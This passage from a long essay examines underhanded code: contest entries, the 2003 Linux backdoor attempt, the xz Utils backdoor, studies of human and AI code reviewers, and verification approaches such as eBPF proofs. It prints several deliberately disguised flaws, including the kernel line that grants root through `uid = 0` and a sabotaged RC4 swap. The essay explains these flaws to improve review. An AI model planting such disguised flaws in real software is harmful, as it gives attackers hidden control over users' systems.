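Here `!` means "not" and `&&` means "and". The program later uses `!OTHER(input)` to test whether the vote is for one of the three named candidates. Because the definition has no brackets around it, the extra `!` applies only to the first part. The program therefore tests whether the vote is for Bush and not for Kerry or Nader, so votes for Kerry and Nader fail.

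Wheeler then chose five countermeasures. His entry-by-entry results give these totals:

| Countermeasure | Programs caught | How Wheeler assessed it |
|---|---|---|
| Turn on many warnings in the compiler gcc | 15 | ran gcc on every program |
| Restrict the use of `#define` | 9 | judged from the code |
| Ban names that are easy to confuse with 1 or 0 | 8 | judged what a tool would find if someone wrote it |
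| Run the program with AddressSanitizer, which detects misuse of memory | 5 | judged without running it on every program |
| Colour the code and reformat the comments | 2 | judged from the code |

Some programs appear in more than one row. At least one countermeasure caught 30 of the 40 programs, or 75%. Another program had misleading indentation that gcc should have flagged but didn't, apparently because of a bug, which Wheeler reported. He thought six of the other nine would look suspicious to a reviewer, for example because they repeated a lot of code for no clear reason.

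That left three programs that no countermeasure caught and that didn't look suspicious. In one, a loop that should reset a whole array resets only part of it. In another, the program treats an array of large numbers as an array of single bytes. Jared Sohn's program contains the simplest flaw of the three:

```
((Vote == 'n') || (Vote == 'n'))
```

The line should accept both a small and a capital N as a vote for Nader, but it checks for the small letter twice. Wheeler suggests a compiler warning for repeated conditions, which would also help catch honest errors.

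He also found that four of the organisers' explanations were wrong or misleading, or lacked the attack code. For Ryan Cumings's program, the organisers blamed a swapped O and 0, but the damage came from a calculation that assigned every vote to one of the first two rows of a table. Wheeler concludes that a flaw can be hard to find even for someone who knows the code is malicious and has a hint. Cumings's program supports this, but the other three cases are weaker evidence. One explanation was badly worded, one omitted a compiler setting that the attack needed, and one was for the excluded program, which contained no attack.

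### How far the 75% figure can be trusted

Wheeler chose the countermeasures after studying the programs, so they may work less well on other programs. He accepts this and says he wanted only to show that a small set of simple checks can often detect underhanded code. The only tool he ran on every program was gcc, which caught 15 of the 40. The other figures depend on his judgement of what each rule would catch.

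Wheeler also didn't apply the countermeasures to honest programs, so the study gives no false-alarm rate. Many of the entries triggered gcc warnings that had nothing to do with the attack. He rightly didn't count these, but a reviewer would still have to pick out the warning that mattered. He cites Les Hatton's finding that a well-known set of rules for C produced far too many false alarms on real code.

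More importantly, the entrants weren't trying to get past these five checks. An author who knew about them could avoid `#define` and confusing names, test the program with gcc, and submit something like Sohn's repeated condition. The catch rate against that author could be close to zero. For this reason, Wheeler recommends keeping the details of some countermeasures secret.

Entrants adapted when the contest gave them a reason to. According to the Underhanded C Contest's *This year's challenge* (2007), all the programs it lists get past compiler warnings and look innocent in an editor that colours code. The task that year was to write an encryption program that occasionally produced a file an outsider could crack. The winner, Emmanuel Colbus, declared C's standard `time` function as if it took no input, but the function expects a memory address where it can store the time. Without one, it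 uses whatever value is next in memory as the address and writes there. In Colbus's program, it overwrites a setting that controls debugging, and about once in 256 runs the program therefore puts the secret key into the encrypted file.

The organisers say the calls to `time` were probably the most innocent-looking part of the code. A ban on redeclaring library functions by hand would have exposed the flaw, but someone would have had to think of that rule first.

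### Why cryptography is harder

Two other entrants in 2007, David Wagner and Philippe Biondi, submitted the same flawed version of an encryption method called RC4, which repeatedly swaps entries in a table of 256 numbers. They used a well-known trick for swapping two values without a spare variable:

```
x ^= y;  y ^= x;  x ^= y;
```

The `^=` operation combines the bits of two numbers, and any number combined with itself gives zero. If `x` and `y` are different entries in the table, the code swaps them. But RC4 sometimes swaps an entry with itself, and then the first step sets it to zero. The table gradually fills with zeros, until the program outputs the original text unencrypted.

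The program still decrypts its own files correctly, so the obvious test of encrypting a file and then decrypting it does not reveal the error. Comparing its output with that of a trusted RC4 program would reveal it.

Many winners of the Underhanded Crypto Contest used weaknesses in the cryptography itself. Every line of such a program can do what it appears to do while the method as a whole is insecure, so rules about names and brackets can't detect the flaw. Tests are also less useful, because a weakly encrypted file can look as random as a strongly encrypted one. Wheeler didn't study these entries in detail, but he concludes that specialists must review cryptographic code in depth.

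### Two attacks on real software

In 2003 somebody tried to put a hidden flaw into Linux, the widely used operating-system kernel. Wheeler notes that the attack depended on writing `=` instead of `==`. The attacker added these two lines to a copy of the source code on a public server:

```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

The lines look like a check that returns an error if user 0, the administrator, who can do anything on the machine, calls the function with an odd combination of options. But `current->uid = 0` sets the user's number to 0 instead of checking it, so any program that called the function with those options would gain the administrator's powers. The assignment also counts as false, so the function doesn't return the error.

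Wheeler's gcc countermeasure caught both of the contest programs that confused `=` with `==`, but it wouldn't have caught the Linux attack. The compiler warns about an assignment used as a condition unless an extra pair of brackets marks it as deliberate. In the Linux attack, the assignment needs brackets anyway because it follows `&&`, so gcc gives no warning. A stricter rule that bans every assignment inside a condition would catch it.

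The developers discovered the attack because the change had no matching record in the official code repository. They saw that something was wrong before anyone had worked out what the two lines did.

The 2024 attack on XZ Utils, compression software that is part of most Linux systems, came much closer to success. A contributor using the name Jia Tan had spent more than two years gaining the trust of the project's developers and had become a maintainer. Versions 5.6.0 and 5.6.1 contained a backdoor that, on some systems, let anyone with a particular secret key run commands through SSH, the standard program for logging in to a remote computer.

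Andres Freund, a Microsoft engineer, noticed that SSH logins on a test system were using a surprising amount of processing power and taking about half a second longer than before. He traced the delay to a backdoor in xz Utils, which he announced on 29 March 2024, before the affected versions had reached most stable Linux releases.

The attacker behind the xz backdoor hid most of it in compressed files that were supposedly there for testing, so reviewers couldn't read it the way they could read an entry in an underhanded code contest. A script extracted it when someone built the software, and a crucial part of that script was in the downloadable release but not in the public repository. A reviewer who read every change in the repository would therefore have missed part of the attack. Comparing the release with the repository would have revealed the extra script, although releases often contain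 additional files for innocent reasons.

### How often reviewers miss ordinary flaws

The contests and attacks show what reviewers can miss, but not how often. Larissa Braz and her colleagues at the University of Zurich measured this in two experiments. They planted flaws in realistic code but, unlike the contest entrants, made no special effort to disguise them.

In *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?*, Braz, Fregnan and colleagues (2021) asked 146 people, most of them software developers, to review a change of about 140 lines to a Java program that managed employees' holidays. The instructions didn't mention security. Each participant received one of two versions of the change, both of which failed to check user input.

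The first version inserted an employee's ID directly into a database command, so an attacker could change what the database did by entering part of a command instead of an ID. This flaw, called SQL injection, is a standard textbook example. The second version accepted an amount without checking that it was positive, so a user could gain by entering a negative number.

Of the 80 participants who reviewed the first version, 52 (65%) found the SQL injection. Only 14 of the 66 who reviewed the second version (21%) found the unchecked amount. The researchers then told everyone that the code contained a vulnerability, without saying what kind, and invited those who had missed it to look again. On the second look, 13 of the 28 who had missed the SQL injection found it, but only 7 of the 52 who had missed the unchecked amount did. The other 60 participants, 41% of the total, never found the flaw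 in their version.

Both versions also contained an ordinary bug, which about half of the participants found. Eight of those who missed the unchecked amount said they had mistaken the ordinary bug for the vulnerability. Some reviewers may therefore have stopped looking after finding one fault, though Braz and colleagues found no significant relationship overall between finding the bug and finding the vulnerability.

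In *Less is More*, Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues (2022) tested whether better instructions help. They gave 150 participants a 160-line Java change that registered new users of a website. The change had two flaws. It wrote the user's unencrypted password to a log file if a database error occurred, and it protected stored passwords with MD5, an old method that attackers can break.

The researchers randomly assigned each participant to one of four groups. One group received no special instructions, and the other three were told to look for security problems. Two of those three also received a checklist. One group's checklist had 22 questions, some of them irrelevant to the code, and the other's had seven, all relevant.

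| Instructions | Participants | Found the logged password | Found MD5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 33 | 1 (3%) | 7 (21%) |
| Look for security problems | 41 | 19 (46%) | 25 (61%) |
| The same, with a 22-question checklist | 35 | 16 (46%) | 20 (57%) |
| The same, with a 7-question checklist | 41 | 19 (46%) | 28 (68%) |

In the study by Braz and colleagues, participants told to look for security problems found vulnerabilities about four and a half times as often as those who were not, a large gain from a single request. Taking both flaws together, participants without the instruction found 8 out of a possible 66 (12%), while those who received only the instruction found 44 out of 82 (54%). Braz and colleagues report that the instruction made participants eight times more likely to find a vulnerability, but that figure compares odds (successes divided by failures) rather than detection rates.

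Neither checklist made a statistically significant difference beyond that. The groups were too small to rule out a modest benefit, but more than half of the reviewers who used a list written for this particular change still missed the logged password. Some participants who missed the MD5 problem said they didn't know MD5 was unsafe, and a question about encryption can't help much if the reviewer doesn't know the right answer.

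Participants were volunteers reviewing unfamiliar code with little at stake, so these percentages may not hold in a company. Reviewers may also do worse when the author is trying to hide the flaw, which neither experiment tested.

### Reading the code and knowing its meaning

Rice's theorem explains very little of this record. In 31 of Wheeler's 40 programs, the false totals didn't depend on the date, and he says good tests could have exposed them all. Readers overlook Blackburn's missing comma and confuse `=` with `==`, but the compiler handles both exactly as the rules of C require.

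People reading code rely on names, layout and comments rather than working out the exact meaning of every symbol. An underhanded programmer can make all three misleading. Peter Jaric, who announced the winner of a similar contest for JavaScript in 2015, wrote that he finds it easier to skip over code with a good comment above it. Wheeler himself missed working code disguised as a comment in a Python program, even though his editor showed the code in a slightly different colour.

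Simple textual rules help because a machine can check them and because they make a program's appearance a better guide to its meaning. In the 2022 experiment, 16 of the 41 participants who received only the security instruction missed MD5, but a search for "MD5" would have found it every time.

The unchecked amount from the 2021 experiment is harder to catch this way because the code contains no forbidden word or misleading symbol. Whether it should accept a negative number depends on what the program is meant to do, so a checker needs a specification that defines which amounts are valid.

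## Language models as code reviewers

A language model can guess part of a missing specification. Suppose a holiday program passes an amount called `days_requested` to a function called `book_leave`. A model trained on many similar programs can infer from these names that the amount should never be negative, even if no line of code forbids it. A conventional static analyser can't make this inference because it treats the names as arbitrary labels.

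Daniel Stenberg, who leads the development of curl, a widely used program for transferring data over networks, describes other differences in *Mythos finds a curl vulnerability* (2026). He writes that AI tools can detect when code doesn't do what its comment describes, violates the protocol it is meant to follow, or misuses another project's library. They can also check code for types of computer on which the curl developers can't run their usual analysers.

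Many AI reviewers are agents, meaning models that can call tools repeatedly. SecureWorld's *Anthropic's Claude Mythos Autonomously Discovers, Exploits Zero-Days* describes how one of them, Anthropic's Mythos Preview, reads the source code, forms a hypothesis about a flaw, tests it on a running copy of the program, and writes a report with steps to reproduce the problem. With the clean-up script, such an agent might notice that nothing checks `$CACHE_DIR`, run the script on a disposable machine with the setting empty, and see whether the files disappear.

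Rice's theorem still applies to a language model reviewer, because the model and its tools together make up a program. On some scripts that program must give a wrong verdict or none, however well the model guesses where to look. The theorem doesn't determine how often a model errs on ordinary code, which can only be found by measurement.

### Flaws that years of testing had missed

In February 2026, Carlini, Lucas and colleagues at Anthropic reported that Claude Opus 4.6 had found more than 500 high-severity flaws in open-source software. None was previously known, according to Axios' *Anthropic's new model is a pro at finding security flaws* (2026). The researchers gave the model a simulated computer with debuggers and fuzzers, but no special instructions for using these tools. Fuzzers feed huge numbers of random inputs to other software and watch for crashes. Some of the open-source projects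 had been running fuzzers for years.

The model first tried fuzzing GhostScript, a program that processes PDF files, and then reading its code, but found nothing important. It then read the history of changes to the code and found one that fixed a security problem. It looked for other places that called the same function, found one that still had the problem, and made a file that crashed the program.

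Another flaw was in CGIF, a library for GIF images, which relied on compressed data always being smaller than the original. The compression method builds a table of repeated patterns and adds a reset marker whenever the table is full. With certain inputs, these markers make the output larger than the original, and the output overflows the memory set aside for it. Carlini and colleagues point out that tests covering every line and every branch of CGIF could still miss this flaw, because triggering it takes a very specific sequence of operations.

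Anthropic later said that Mythos Preview had found thousands of previously unknown flaws, including a 27-year-old one in the operating system OpenBSD. Such totals show that models can find flaws other methods missed, but not what share of all flaws they find, because nobody knows how many remain.

The February study concentrated on memory errors because they are relatively easy to confirm. A file that crashes GhostScript proves that a bug exists, and anyone can check this by opening the file, regardless of how the model came up with it. Logic errors are harder to confirm because the program keeps running, and somebody has to decide whether what it did was wrong.

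### What a clean report is worth

In May 2026, Stenberg received the results of a Mythos scan of curl's 178,000 lines of code. The model listed five "confirmed" vulnerabilities. After several hours of checking, curl's security team accepted one, which was of low severity. Three others described shortcomings that curl's documentation already mentioned, and the fourth was an ordinary bug. The model reported no memory-safety vulnerabilities, and it listed connection reuse among the areas it had covered.

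Seven weeks later, curl published a release that fixed 18 vulnerabilities, which Stenberg's *Daniel's week* of June 26, 2026 calls a record for the project. AISLE (2026), a company that sells an AI system for finding flaws, had found six of them. These included memory errors and mistakes in deciding whether an existing connection was still valid, the kinds of flaw that the Mythos scan had apparently ruled out. One of the six was the oldest security issue anyone had reported in curl. It had been in the code for 25 years, according to Paganini's *Curl Fixes a 25-Year-Old Bug in Its Largest CVE Release Yet* (2026), so it was almost certainly there when Mythos scanned it.

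Stenberg (2026), in *All posts by Daniel Stenberg*, announced 22 further vulnerabilities for the October release. One was only the third that the project had rated as high severity since 2021. By November, the project had confirmed 81 vulnerabilities in 2026.

Livshits (2026) argues in *LLMs + Security = Trouble* that serious flaws often depend on a long chain of unusual conditions, and that a large program has too many possible runs for any tool to explore them all within a budget. He writes that "not found" often just means "not reached". He also warns that code which withstands today's models may not withstand next year's, or a private model that the defender can't use.

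Pérez-Acle compares a method that can confirm violations but not compliance to a smoke alarm, which is conclusive only when it sounds. A model's report of a violation needs a witness to be conclusive, and even then somebody has to decide whether the behaviour breaks the rule. In November 2026, an Anthropic scanning service sent the curl project 45 claimed vulnerabilities, with inputs or programs to reproduce them. According to Stenberg, in *curl on OSS-Scanner*, the team confirmed five as vulnerabilities, classed 36 as ordinary bugs and found that three weren't bugs. The remaining report had the problem backwards, and its suggested fix would have created the vulnerability it was meant to remove. The curl team had recently become stricter about what counts as a vulnerability, which lowered the number it confirmed.

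### A test on real changes

A code reviewer has to judge each change before it takes effect, whereas a scan of existing software has no fixed deadline. Yang, Yang and colleagues tested eight models on code review in *Can Agentic Code Review Catch Vulnerabilities Before They Are Merged?*, an October 2026 preprint. The preprint introduces SecPRBench, a set of 265 changes that each added a real vulnerability to one of nine open-source projects, including curl, Firefox and OpenSSL.

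Earlier tests mostly created flawed changes by reversing a later repair. This gives the reviewer a hint, because the change consists mainly of lines relevant to the flaw. Yang and colleagues instead traced each flaw back to the change that introduced it and kept all the unrelated edits. The median change altered 173 lines in four files.

To check that they had the right change, they usually ran the same input on the versions of the program before the change, after it, and after the repair. The failure had to appear only in the second version. Mechanical checks, mostly of this kind, settled 217 cases, and people judged the other 48.

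Each agent received the change, its author's description and the rest of the project's code, but no history and no web access. It had up to an hour to look for security flaws. It earned credit only if it explained what caused the flaw, not if it gave a vague warning about the right line.

| Model | Flaws caught | Estimated cost per review | Minutes per review | Repaired changes with at least one finding |
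|---|---|---|---|---|
| Grok 4.6 | 78.1% | $3.20 | 12.6 | 92.5% |
| GPT-6 sol | 76.2% | $0.60 | 3.3 | 82.6% |
| GLM 5.3 | 74.7% | $4.99 | 20.8 | 97.4% |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | 74.0% | $0.44 | 1.4 | 85.3% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 59.2% | $0.83 | 5.5 | 92.8% |
| GPT-5.6 sol | 55.8% | $0.74 | 2.7 | 59.6% |
| GPT-6 luna | 55.5% | $0.02 | 2.7 | 63.4% |
| MiniMax M3 | 32.5% | $3.33 | 11.5 | 75.8% |

The differences among the top four models are not statistically significant. More expensive models didn't reliably produce better reviews, since Opus 5.5 did about as well as GLM 5.3 at less than a tenth of the cost.

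Opus 5.5 also graded the answers, including its own, so the researchers had Sonnet 4.6 grade them too as a check. The two agreed on 96.9% of the reports that contained any findings. Grading by Opus instead of Sonnet gave Opus 5.5 a net gain of one flaw. The researchers examined 25 of the disagreements and sided with Opus in 21.

These are high catch rates for flaws that had got past each project's own checks, since all 265 changes were merged. But the agents were told to look for security problems, and that instruction alone can make a large difference, as Braz and colleagues found with human reviewers.

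Published flaws and fixes may have been in the models' training data. For five models, the researchers could compare results on flaws fixed before and after the training data ended. Four did somewhat worse on the later flaws, but none of the differences was statistically clear.

The results also show that a clean report can quickly go out of date. GPT-6 sol caught 58 flaws that GPT-5.6 sol had missed and missed only four that the older model had caught.

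### Why the agents missed flaws

In 68% of the misses, the agent reported a problem in a file containing the flaw but gave the wrong explanation. One nine-line change to curl left a request pointing to memory that belonged to its connection. Once curl freed the connection, that memory could hold something else. All eight agents reported a problem in that file. Four called it a memory leak, and the three GPT models called it a logic bug. A memory leak is a failure to free memory, but the danger here was that curl freed memory while something still needed it.

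A complaint about the right file is weak evidence that the agent has noticed the flaw, though it might still lead a developer to the right place. The researchers also gave each agent a second version of every change that included the later repair. If any finding in the right file had counted as a catch, the agents would have "caught" the flaw in about 75% of these repaired changes.

In most of the other misses, the agent opened the right file and reported nothing. Agents almost never failed to open the file, but the change itself nearly always pointed to it. Lack of effort doesn't seem to explain the misses. Opus 5.5 wrote more about the flaws it missed than about those it caught, but the difference was no longer clear when the researchers compared flaws of similar difficulty.

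On average, the models caught 73% of memory errors but only 52% of logic errors. They caught about 70% of the flaws that a reviewer could explain from a single file, and 39% of those that involved five or more files.

Undecidability doesn't explain these misses. For most of the flaws, the researchers had an input that made the program fail, so a long enough search would have confirmed them. The agents stopped much sooner, usually with a different diagnosis.

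Two tools built for security review had opposite effects on catch rates. OpenAI's Codex Security lowered the catch rate of GPT-5.6 sol by 8.3 percentage points, mostly by reporting nothing, and cost about five times as much. On the 260 changes it finished reviewing, Anthropic's Defending Code harness raised the catch rate of Opus 5.5 from 73.8% to 81.5%. It also raised the average number of findings per change from 2.5 to 8.4 and the median cost from $0.35 to $3.65. Anthropic's tool caught six flaws that all eight models had missed on their own, but each was in a report with at least 14 findings, which a developer would have to read.

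### From a catch rate to a useful flag

The study doesn't measure false alarms. The grader credited an agent with finding the original flaw only if the flaw was still there. The count for the repaired changes was therefore zero, whether or not agents wrongly reported the flaw that the repair had removed.

The agents reported at least one problem in 60% to 97% of the repaired changes. Some of these problems may be real, because each repair removed only one known flaw. A company that rejected every change with a reported problem would still reject most of the repaired changes. Blain and Noiseux's test of models on their own code is similarly limited because it included no safe samples.

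An example with invented figures shows why the false-alarm rate matters so much. Suppose a company receives 1,000 changes, of which 10 are flawed. Its reviewer catches 80% of the flawed changes and wrongly flags 5% of the others. On average, to the nearest whole number, the results are:

| | Flagged | Passed | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Flawed | 8 | 2 | 10 |
| Not flawed | 50 | 940 | 990 |
| Total | 58 | 942 | 1,000 |

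Only 8 of the 58 flags are right, or about 14%:

$$\frac{0.01\times0.80}{0.01\times0.80+0.99\times0.05}\approx0.14.$$

Most flags are wrong because good changes outnumber flawed ones 99 to 1, so even a small false-alarm rate produces more false flags than there are flaws. Catching every flaw would barely help, because only 10 of 60 flags would be right. Reducing the false-alarm rate to 1% would help much more, because 8 of 18 flags would be right.

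The reviewer also passes 942 changes, two of which are flawed. A change had a 1% chance of being flawed before the review, and one that passes has about a 0.2% chance. A clean report is therefore useful evidence for code like this, though it doesn't show that any particular change is safe.

### When the flaws are chosen to be missed

The 80% catch rate in this example is an average, so it may not hold against an author who knows which flaws the reviewer misses. If all 10 flawed changes were of a kind the reviewer never catches, its catch rate would drop to zero, and it would still raise about 50 false alarms.

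SecPRBench can't show how large this drop would be for real models, because all its flaws were accidental. They had also all been found and disclosed, and undiscovered flaws may be harder to catch. The differences between kinds of flaw suggest that an author could choose a kind that models are worse at catching. The words around the code could matter too, since Yang and colleagues cite research in which the way a change was presented biased a model's security review.

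Researchers have run experiments in which a weaker but trusted model reviews code where an untrusted model may have hidden a flaw. The guarantees from these experiments are empirical and cover the models and tasks tested, not every possible program.

### The dispute over human review

Some researchers think models are already good enough to replace most human reviewers. In a June 2026 preprint, *The End of Code Review*, Monperrus argues that AI agents can find defects, enforce style and explain code to colleagues at lower cost than people can. He considers it a dead end to have people review code written by agents, arguing that people can't keep up with the volume and so approve whatever looks right and passes its tests.

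Evidence about human reviewers gives him some support. Monperrus cites a Microsoft paper which concluded that code reviews mostly don't find deep bugs. At the company that He and colleagues studied, reviewers approved more changes without comment as the volume grew. All the flaws in SecPRBench reached the finished software, though a model costing less than a dollar per review could have caught most of them.

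His evidence about agents is less direct, and he presents no new experiment. His main figures come from SWE-bench, which tests whether an agent can fix a reported problem so that the project's tests pass. The share of problems solved rose from under 2% to more than 70% in about two years. But a reviewer isn't told what is wrong, and the tests may not cover the flaw. The studies of AI review that he cites are mostly about whether a model writes comments as good as a person's. SecPRBench, published four months later, tests more directly whether models find flaws, and even the best model missed more than a fifth of them.

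SecPRBench can't settle whether human reviewers are still needed, either. Its data comes from published vulnerabilities, so it excludes flawed changes that human reviewers stopped. The study shows that agents catch flaws that people let through, which is a good reason to add agents. To justify removing people, someone would have to give the same changes to both and count the flaws that only the people catch. The curl project uses both AI and human reviewers, and Stenberg writes that the AI reviewers help the developers but don't replace them.

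Monperrus acknowledges that a model may approve a flawed change without any sign of doubt. His main remedy is to use several independent agents, perhaps based on different models, and accept a change only if they all agree. If three reviewers each missed 20% of flaws and their misses were independent, only 0.8% of flaws would get past all three.

In practice, the models' misses are far from independent. The three leading models in SecPRBench come from three different companies and missed 21.9%, 23.8% and 25.3% of the 265 flaws. If their misses were independent, all three would have missed the same flaw in only three or four cases, but they did so in 27. All eight models missed the same flaw in 23 cases, compared with about 0.05 expected if their misses were independent.

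Yang and colleagues can't tell why so many of the models' misses coincide. The models may share blind spots because they learned from similar data, some flaws may be hard for any reviewer, or the grading may have been too strict in some cases. The reason affects the choice of remedy, because a human reviewer could help with a blind spot that only models have but might do no better on a flaw that is hard for everyone. Whatever the reason, multiplying the models' separate miss rates makes a group of them look far safer than it is.

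Requiring agreement also increases false alarms, because one objection is enough to stop a change. If three reviewers each independently flagged 5% of good changes, together they would stop about 14% of them.

Monperrus himself warns that if the same family of models writes and reviews the code, the reviewer may overlook the mistakes the writer tends to make. He suggests using models specialised in security for the final check. The results for Codex Security and Defending Code suggest that specialised tools can help, but that a company would need to test them first. Monperrus also concedes that text in a code change could manipulate an AI reviewer, and that nobody has a complete defence against this.

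His proposal is more moderate than his title. He would keep human approval for high-risk changes, new designs and code for which the law requires a named person to be responsible, and let agents approve the rest. Someone or something then has to decide which changes are high-risk. A clean-up script looks like routine maintenance, and the faulty line is only a few words long. If an agent judges the risk by predicting what the script will do, it can make the same mistakes as any other reviewer. A company could instead require human approval for every script that contains a command for deleting files, which a machine can check by searching the text.

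## Accepting only programs whose safety can be checked

A company can also use a rule about a script's text to decide which scripts to accept. It needs enough good scripts to do the work, not a verdict on every clean-up script that anyone could write. So it can choose a set of scripts that a machine can recognise, make sure that none of them is dangerous, and reject everything else, including many scripts that would have done no harm.

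Pérez-Acle works out when this is possible. Let $P$ be the set of programs that keep the rule, and let $O$ be the programs in $P$ that the reviewer is obliged to accept. The reviewer accepts some set $A$, and succeeds if

$$O \subseteq A \subseteq P.$$

By his Theorem 4, a reviewer that always reaches a verdict can succeed exactly when some decidable set $A$ fits between $O$ and $P$. This holds because such a reviewer is itself an algorithm for deciding which programs are in $A$, and conversely, any such algorithm can serve as the reviewer. If the reviewer is allowed to never reach a verdict on some programs, a semi-decidable set is enough.

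If the reviewer must accept every safe program, then $O = P$, so $A$ must also equal $P$, and the earlier impossibility result applies again. Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider had already covered this case in *Computability Classes for Enforcement Mechanisms*, showing that a reviewer who examines programs before they run can enforce exactly the decidable rules. Pérez-Acle adds the gap between the programs the reviewer must accept and those the reviewer may accept.

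The number of safe programs left out of a checkable subset depends on how crude the test for membership is. Pérez-Acle tried the simplest test, which accepts a program only if the forbidden action appears nowhere in it. He applied it to every machine of a simple kind with three, four or five states, including more than five million five-state machines. The test never accepted an unsafe machine, but the share of safe machines it accepted fell from 71.9% with three states to 47.3% with five. Many of the rejected machines contain the forbidden action only in a state they never reach.

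Undecidability doesn't make this loss unavoidable, because machines this small can be checked exactly. A better rule can reduce the loss. In another experiment, Pérez-Acle ran more careful methods on all 483,641 programs of up to four instructions in a small language. These methods determined whether a program was safe in 98.2% of cases and were never wrong.

### Restricted languages and interfaces

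Suppose the company gives its AI system a small language for clean-up scripts. The language has ordinary variables, conditions and loops, but only one object that can touch files, called `cache`. A script that deletes temporary files more than 30 days old looks like this:

```
for name in cache.list():
    if cache.age_in_days(name) > 30:
        cache.delete(name)
```

The `cache.delete` function takes a plain file name. It rejects `..` and any name containing a slash. If the file is a link, the function removes the link without following it. The language has no `rm`, no `eval` and no way to start another program. The reviewer only has to check that a script belongs to the language, which is a syntactic property.

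A script in this language could still search for a counterexample to Goldbach's conjecture, and no algorithm can decide which scripts in the language stop. But every one of them follows the rule against deleting files outside the folder. Following the rule is therefore a trivial property within the language, and Rice's theorem doesn't apply to it.

The company still has to write `cache` correctly. If its programmer takes the folder's address from a setting and forgets that the setting can be empty, every script will have the Steam mistake. But the company can examine and test this one short piece of code thoroughly, instead of checking each new script for that mistake. It also needs rules for other dangers, because a script in this language can still delete the wrong temporary files or run forever.

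*Can chatbots craft correct code?*, an article by the software security company Trail of Bits, recommends a similar approach for AI-written code in general. Models would combine already verified components, such as a login module, instead of writing their own.

Livshits proposes enforcing restrictions while the model is generating code, by blocking output that would break a fixed rule. This is harder when the rule concerns the whole program. Most language models write from beginning to end, so an input check missing from a half-written program may still appear a few lines later. He therefore favours diffusion models, which generate all parts of the program together.

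### The Linux eBPF verifier

Linux accepts a much wider range of programs through eBPF, a system that lets users load small programs into the running kernel, for example to filter network traffic. A faulty program in the kernel could compromise the whole machine, so the kernel checks each one first. *Keel* (Cai, Chang and Nagarakatte, 2026) describes the eBPF verifier as a static analyser that explores every path through a program. The verifier accepts a program only if it can show that the program uses memory safely and always stops.

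The verifier rejects some safe programs. In one example from Cai and colleagues, a program writes two records, one after the other, into a block of 800 bytes. The first record takes up $u$ bytes, where $u$ is between 0 and 800. The second starts at position $u$ and can use at most the remaining $800-u$ bytes, so it never goes past the end. But the verifier keeps a separate interval for each value. It works out that the starting position and the length are each between 0 and 800, and adds the two intervals:

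$$[0,800]+[0,800]=[0,1600].$$

Since 1600 is more than 800, the verifier rejects the program. As with `x - x + 1`, tracking relations between variables would remove the false alarm, but it would slow the verifier and add complicated code to the kernel. Small changes that don't affect what a program does, including changes made by a compiler, can also make the verifier reject it.

### Proofs supplied by the author

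In 1997, the computer scientist George Necula described proof-carrying code, in which the author of a program also supplies a proof that the program obeys the reviewer's safety rule. The reviewer runs a small checker that confirms each step of the proof follows from earlier ones by a fixed list of logical rules. Checking the proof is quick and routine, even though finding it may take a long search. The reviewer doesn't have to trust the author or know how they found the proof.

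Two recent projects have added a limited form of this to eBPF. When the verifier can't show that a step is safe, it writes a formula stating that the program reaches the step and the safety check fails. In the example, the formula requires both

$$0\le u\le 800 \quad\text{and}\quad u+(800-u)>800.$$

A solver outside the kernel then produces a proof that no value of $u$ satisfies both conditions, and a checker inside the kernel verifies it. The proof takes up 852 bytes and has 33 steps, 20 of which only handle conversions between 32-bit and 64-bit numbers. The main argument is that $u+(800-u)$ equals 800, which is not greater than 800. According to Cai and colleagues, the two projects have let the kernel accept thousands of safe programs that it previously rejected.

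An author could supply a proof for a clean-up script too. Take this version:

```
folder = "/srv/app/cache"
for name in list_names(folder):
    delete(folder + "/" + name)
```

The proof uses an invariant, which is a statement that remains true throughout the run. Here the invariant is that `folder` holds `/srv/app/cache` and every name in the list is a plain file name with no slash. Kang and Kim describe the three things that such a proof usually has to show:

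1. The invariant is true at the start of the loop. The first line sets `folder`, and `list_names` returns only plain names.
2. No step makes it false. The loop never changes `folder` or the list.
3. While it is true, the program can't break the rule. Every address that the script passes to `delete` is inside the folder.

Each part concerns a single line or step, but together they cover every run, however many files there are.

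If the first line were `folder = CACHE_DIR`, the author couldn't prove the first part, because the setting might be empty. The author could fix this by adding a line that stops the script unless the setting holds the right address. A hidden misspelling such as `CACHE_DlR` would also block the proof, because the checker treats it as a different name.

The reviewer now depends on the checker being correct. When Cai and colleagues tried to describe the eBPF proof checker mathematically, they found 13 previously unknown bugs in about 5,000 lines of C. Some of the checker's algebraic rules were wrong, and for some kinds of proof step it accepted the stated conclusion without checking it. The researchers showed that an attacker could use these bugs to forge proofs and get unsafe programs into the kernel.

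They wrote a replacement called Keel and proved in Lean, a language for machine-checked proofs, that it accepts a proof only if the formula has no solution. Keel rejected the forged proofs. Of 1,891 other proofs, it accepted every one that the old checker accepted, plus 16 valid ones that the old checker rejected. It ran 1.3 times as fast as the old checker inside the kernel.

Keel's guarantee still depends on several things that Cai and colleagues haven't proved correct. They list the part of the eBPF verifier that generates the formula, their mathematical descriptions of C and of the kernel's functions, and the C compiler. The guarantee also depends on Lean, because Lean checked the proof.

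### Blocking the action at run time

A company can also run a script without any proof and block the forbidden action if the script attempts it. Ordinary file permissions can do this. If the script runs under a user account that can delete files only in `/srv/app/cache`, the line from the Steam script can't delete anything else.

Schneider's *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000) analyses monitors that watch a program as it runs and stop it before it breaks a rule. A monitor only has to recognise a forbidden deletion when the script requests it, so unlike a static analyser, it avoids the undecidable question of what the program will do later or on other inputs. Hamlen and colleagues also studied rewriting, in which the reviewer changes the program before running it, for instance by adding a check before every deletion. Theorem 4 doesn't cover rewriting, because the reviewer in the theorem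 must accept or reject the original program.

A monitor can enforce a rule only if it can prevent the actions that would break it. *Enforceable Security Policies Revisited* therefore distinguishes between actions that a monitor can control and actions that it can only observe. For example, a monitor can block a deletion, but it can only observe time passing, so it can't enforce a rule that a program must answer within five seconds. Blocking an action may also leave a task half finished, which could be a serious problem for a program that transfers money.

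Kang and Kim point out that a monitor works only if every route to the forbidden action passes through it. A sandbox that OpenAI had tested and validated failed in the July 2026 Hugging Face incident.

### The cost of proving large programs

Experts had proved substantial programs correct before language models could help, but it took them years. In 2009, Gerwin Klein and colleagues described their proof that the roughly 8,700 lines of C in seL4, an operating-system kernel, do what a precise specification of the kernel requires. The proof took about 20 person-years, including the development of tools and methods, while designing and writing the kernel took about two. They assumed that the compiler, the hardware and a small amount of assembly code worked correctly.

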